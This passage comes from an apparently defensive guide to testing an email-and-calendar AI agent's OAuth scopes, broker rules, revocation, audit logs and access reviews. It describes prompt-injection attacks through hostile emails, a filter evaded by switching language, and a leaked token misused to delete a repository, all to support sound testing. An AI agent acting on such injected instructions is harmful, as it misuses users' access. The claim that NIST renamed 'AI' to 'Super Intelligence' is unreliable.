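Google allows calls that invite a guest or delete an event, though the task needs neither. Only the broker blocks these calls, so the approver accepts the risk that someone who steals the token could make them.

A call can also fail for reasons unrelated to the token's permissions, such as when the tester tries to delete a message that doesn't exist. The tester should therefore first confirm that the call works by making it with a broader token on a spare message.

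A refusal to open the colleague's calendar with a calendar.events.owned token doesn't show whether the service also checks Alice's own rights, because that scope already excludes calendars she doesn't own. A token with the wider calendar.events scope tests those rights separately. This test matters most with a small company's API or MCP server, where the developer's code may check only the type of operation. Palo Alto Networks gives the example of an "editor" role, which permits editing but doesn't determine which documents the user may edit.

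To test revocation, the tester can repeat the call every ten seconds, note when it starts to fail, and then check that the refresh token has stopped working too. Some work may continue even then. Zhou and Zhang point out that a second agent can carry on after the first one's plan has changed, and that stored results can outlast access to their source. The tester should look for both, and for any messages the broker still holds.

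### Why the model should not make the calls

If a tester simply asks the agent to delete an email and it replies that it can't, the tester doesn't know why. The model may have declined, the agent may have no tool for deleting mail, or the broker or Google may have blocked the request. Only a block by Google would also stop a thief with the token, and the model's response can change with different wording or a new version. In Peters-Gill and colleagues' test, for instance, Claude Fable 5 refused more than half of the ordinary tasks, and those refusals were not evidence of tight permissions.

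Zhou and Zhang recommend that evaluations examine both how an agent behaves and which unauthorized effects remain possible. A tester can check for those effects with direct calls, but has to run the whole agent to study its behaviour, for example on a mailbox containing hostile emails.

### What an unexpected success reveals

| Call that should have failed | Likely cause |
|---|---|
| Sending or deleting mail directly | The grant includes a broader scope than the approver thought |
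| Sending or deleting mail through the broker only | The broker lacks a rule and attaches a different, broader credential |
| Inviting a guest through the broker | The broker checks the operation but not its arguments |
| Writing to the colleague's calendar | The service doesn't check the user's own rights, or the colleague has shared the calendar |
| Using an expired token | The service ignores the expiry time or allows a few minutes for inaccurate clocks |
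| Using another service's token | The service doesn't check the audience, so other services could use Alice's tokens there |
| Making a call after revocation | The service accepts signed tokens until they expire or reuses a saved lookup |

To test whether an MCP server checks a token's audience, the tester should use a token from the authorization server that the MCP server relies on. A token from an unrelated company would fail the signature or issuer check, so its rejection would not show whether the server checks the audience.

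A failure on a call the agent needs is also a finding. The approver should ask for the exact missing permission, even if a broader scope is tempting, and then rerun every test in the table.

### How much a clean result proves

A scope check normally gives the same answer every time, so trying different operations is more useful than repeating one forbidden call 600 times. Zhu and colleagues counted 116 methods in Gmail and Google Calendar combined, few enough for a program to try every one on a test account.

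A model's behaviour varies from run to run, and here the number of trials matters. Suppose an attack succeeds with probability p, and the trials are independent. The chance of seeing no success in n trials is (1 − p)^n. To find the highest rate that is still reasonably compatible with a clean result, set that chance to 5% and solve for p:

```
(1 - p)^n = 0.05
p = 1 - 0.05^(1/n) ≈ 3/n
```

The result, 3/n, is the upper end of a 95% confidence range. If the true rate were higher, a clean test would happen less than 5% of the time. The 3 comes from the natural logarithm of 0.05, which is about −3.

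ScopeGate refused all 48 prepared attacks, which gives an upper limit of about 6% on its failure rate. PAuth blocked all 634 wrong calls in its test, which gives a limit of about 0.47%. A tester would need about 3,000 trials without a failure to bring the limit down to 0.1%.

These limits hold only if the trials are independent, and PAuth's 634 calls came from only 100 tasks. If wrong calls from the same task tend to succeed or fail together, the effective number of trials is closer to 100, and the limit rises towards 3%.

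A low success rate per attempt offers little protection against an attacker who can keep trying. At 0.47% per attempt, an attacker who makes 1,000 independent attempts has about a 99% chance of succeeding at least once.

The calculated limit applies only to attacks like those in the test, so it doesn't hold for an adaptive attacker, who changes his method after each failure. For example, a filter might catch every hostile email in English but miss those in Welsh. A test with 634 English emails would find no failures, but an attacker who tried Welsh would succeed and then use it every time, so his success rate might be near 100%.

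The tester should therefore also let someone attack the agent freely and see why each attempt failed, as the language model in ScopeGate's test could. The report should then state how many people tried, for how long and with what information. Reporting their failures as a percentage would make the result look more precise than it is.

### What a log entry should contain

After approval, the log is the main record of how the agent uses its access. Here is a useful entry for one call by Dayplan:

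```
time:       2026-10-13T08:14:07Z
user:       user-4821
agent:      https://dayplan.example
token id:   b407e1d9
scopes:     events:read, events:write
operation:  events.insert
arguments:  calendar=primary, start=2026-10-15T10:00+02:00,
            guests=0, description=0 characters
result:     created event ev-5530
approval:   not required (own calendar, no guests)
source:     message m-2207
```

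The token identifier lets an investigator find every other call made with that token. The approval field should identify the person who approved the call, or the rule that made approval unnecessary. The last field records which email led to the call, so if the event turns out to be fraudulent, the investigator can find the hostile text.

Now suppose that Alice's company connects four programs to its calendar system with one shared API key. The next morning the budget review is gone:

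```
time:       2026-10-14T06:02:51Z
user:       company account
agent:      unknown
token id:   key-03
scopes:     full access
operation:  events.delete
arguments:  calendar=alice, event=ev-5530
result:     deleted
approval:   none recorded
```

Any of the four programs that share the key could have made this call, and so could a thief with a copy of it. The network address might narrow down the source, but not if all four programs run on the same server. Having each program write its name in the request doesn't reliably identify the caller, because anyone with the key can write any name. To block the caller, the company has to cancel the key for all four programs.

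An agent that runs under Alice's login causes a similar problem, because the log shows her name whether she or the agent acted. NIST's *Back to the Future*, an article by staff at the US standards agency, warns that this undermines non-repudiation, meaning evidence strong enough that nobody can later deny an action. The agency considers non-repudiation especially important for payments and health records.

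The broker should write the log, because a misled model could leave out a call or describe it falsely. The broker should also record refused calls, since a sudden run of refusals may be the first sign of an attack. The agent's credentials must not allow it to change the log.

A hash chain makes later changes to a log easier to detect. Each entry includes a hash of the one before it, so altering an old entry breaks the link to the next. An intruder who controls the whole file could recalculate every hash, so the company also has to keep a recent hash somewhere the intruder can't reach.

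If the service keeps its own log, it is worth comparing with the broker's. A call that appears only in the service's log means that someone used the credential without going through the broker.

### The privacy cost of logging arguments

The arguments of a call are often the most useful part of the log and the most private. For Alice's agent, they include event titles and descriptions, and perhaps the words it searched for in her mail. A log that stores them in full holds a second copy of her private data. Administrators may be able to read that copy, and it may still exist after she deletes the original message.

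But a log that leaves out all the arguments records too little. In the attack where the agent copied a doctor's letter into an event, the log would show only that the agent had created an event, as Alice had asked.

A sensible compromise is to store the values that show an action's effect, such as the recipient, the amount and the number of guests, and replace free text with its length. A calendar event with a 6,000-character description would stand out even without the text. The broker can also store a keyed hash of the text, calculated with a secret key. An investigator who has the doctor's letter can then check whether the agent sent exactly that text, although the hashes would not match if even one character had changed. With an ordinary hash, anyone who reads the log could work out short texts such as phone numbers by testing guesses.

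If full arguments are necessary, the company can store them separately, limit who may open them and delete them sooner than the rest of the logs. The logs should include only the token's identifier, never the token itself. The NIST staff list logs among the places where people leave keys and tokens unprotected.

### The regular access review

An agent's access can change after it is approved. Reviewing that access every three months, and after any change to the agent's tools or owner, can catch differences from what was approved.

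The reviewer starts with the service's own list of connected programs, because the company's records may be incomplete. Hutchings and colleagues note that users may forget why they gave a program access. Every grant should have a named owner who can explain what it is for. If nobody can, and the log has no recent calls, the reviewer should revoke it, but only after asking around, because some credentials belong to jobs that run once a year.

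To find scopes that are rarely or never used, the reviewer compares the operations in the log with those that each scope permits. If Dayplan has had calendars:share for three months and has shared a calendar only once, it can give up the scope and request it again when needed. The reviewer also compares the current scopes with those originally approved to see whether later requests have expanded the grant.

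An old scope can also become broader without anyone granting anything. A token usually contains only the scope's name, and the service decides what the name permits. Suppose, in a made-up case, that a calendar service adds an export operation to a scope:

```
events:read at approval:   events.list, events.get
events:read today:         events.list, events.get, events.exportAll
added since approval:      events.exportAll
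```

Alice sees no new consent page, yet her agent's existing token can now copy her whole calendar in one call. To notice this, the reviewer has to compare a copy of the token's footprint saved on the day of approval with one calculated from the current documentation. If the documentation may be out of date, the tester's program can try the new operations directly.

Tools on an MCP server can change in the same way while keeping their names. Zhou and Zhang describe ETDI, a system in which the provider signs each version of a tool's definition together with the permissions the tool requires. A reviewer then has a fixed version to compare with, but the comparison is useful only if the definition describes the tool accurately.

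### What OWASP asks for

OWASP, a security community that publishes free guidance, lists "Identity and Privilege Abuse" third (ASI03) in the 2026 edition of its Top 10 for Agentic Applications, dated 9 December 2025 (OWASP, 2025). Sotiropoulos (2026), one of the list's leaders, describes it in *Agentic Security* as an agent inheriting more authority than it should have.

In his example, a coding assistant holds a powerful GitHub token. During a handover, the token leaks to a coordinating agent that should have few rights. An attacker sends that agent a request, and it uses the token to delete a private repository or make it public. A tester can check for this kind of leak by having the first agent hand a harmless task to the second, then searching the second agent's conversation, memory and files for the first agent's credentials.

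For the whole list, Sotiropoulos recommends tokens tied to one workflow, continuous authorization, strict limits on tools, and approval for individual actions. He also recommends regular attack tests and logging everything along with its origin. Logging everything conflicts with protecting Alice's privacy, and he doesn't resolve that conflict in his slides.

On 2 September 2026 OWASP (2026) announced the *Agent Control Standard (ACS)*, which defines points in an agent platform where other software can inspect the agent's work and enforce rules. The standard is meant to let a company see what an agent can access, what it did and why. The reason is the hardest of these to record because a model's explanation of its own action may be wrong, as the PocketOS case showed.

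### What NIST asks for

NIST's main paper on the subject so far consists largely of questions. In *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) ask how an agent can log its actions in a way nobody can tamper with, and how to link each action to a person's authorization. They also ask how to apply least privilege when nobody can fully predict what an agent will do. The paper is a draft that proposes a project to build and document working examples. The draft received more than 600 formal responses, according to Identiverse's *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*.

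The NIST staff article, which draws on those responses, gives firmer advice. It says each agent should have its own identifier, credentials and permissions, linked to the user or system that operates it. It also favours short-lived, narrowly scoped tokens over static keys, and warns that people who get too many approval requests start clicking "allow" without thinking.

The project is still collecting comments, according to NIST's *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization*. The page now uses "SI", for "Super Intelligence", in place of "AI". NIST has released a summary of the comments, but the page lists no finished practice guide. The project will start with companies' own agents and may later cover agents from untrusted outsiders, which public websites have to deal with.

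### What has the force of a requirement

Neither OWASP's list nor NIST's concept paper is law. Otsuka and colleagues rate both as "directional", meaning the ideas are sound but lack instructions for applying them. This seems a little harsh on OWASP, since a developer can act on advice such as giving each workflow its own token. But an auditor would struggle to give a system a clear pass or fail against either document.

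A contract can make guidance binding, for example if a customer requires a supplier to address every item on OWASP's list. The word "must" in the MCP specification binds developers in a more limited way, because they have to follow it only if they want their software to conform to the standard.

Few laws specifically address AI agents' identities. As of April 2026, Otsuka and colleagues found no US federal law on AI identity and no country with a framework for liability when autonomous agents cause harm. They read the EU's AI Act as not assigning responsibility when an agent exceeds its authority. General laws still apply. For example, a company covered by the GDPR must follow it when logging personal data from Alice's mail.
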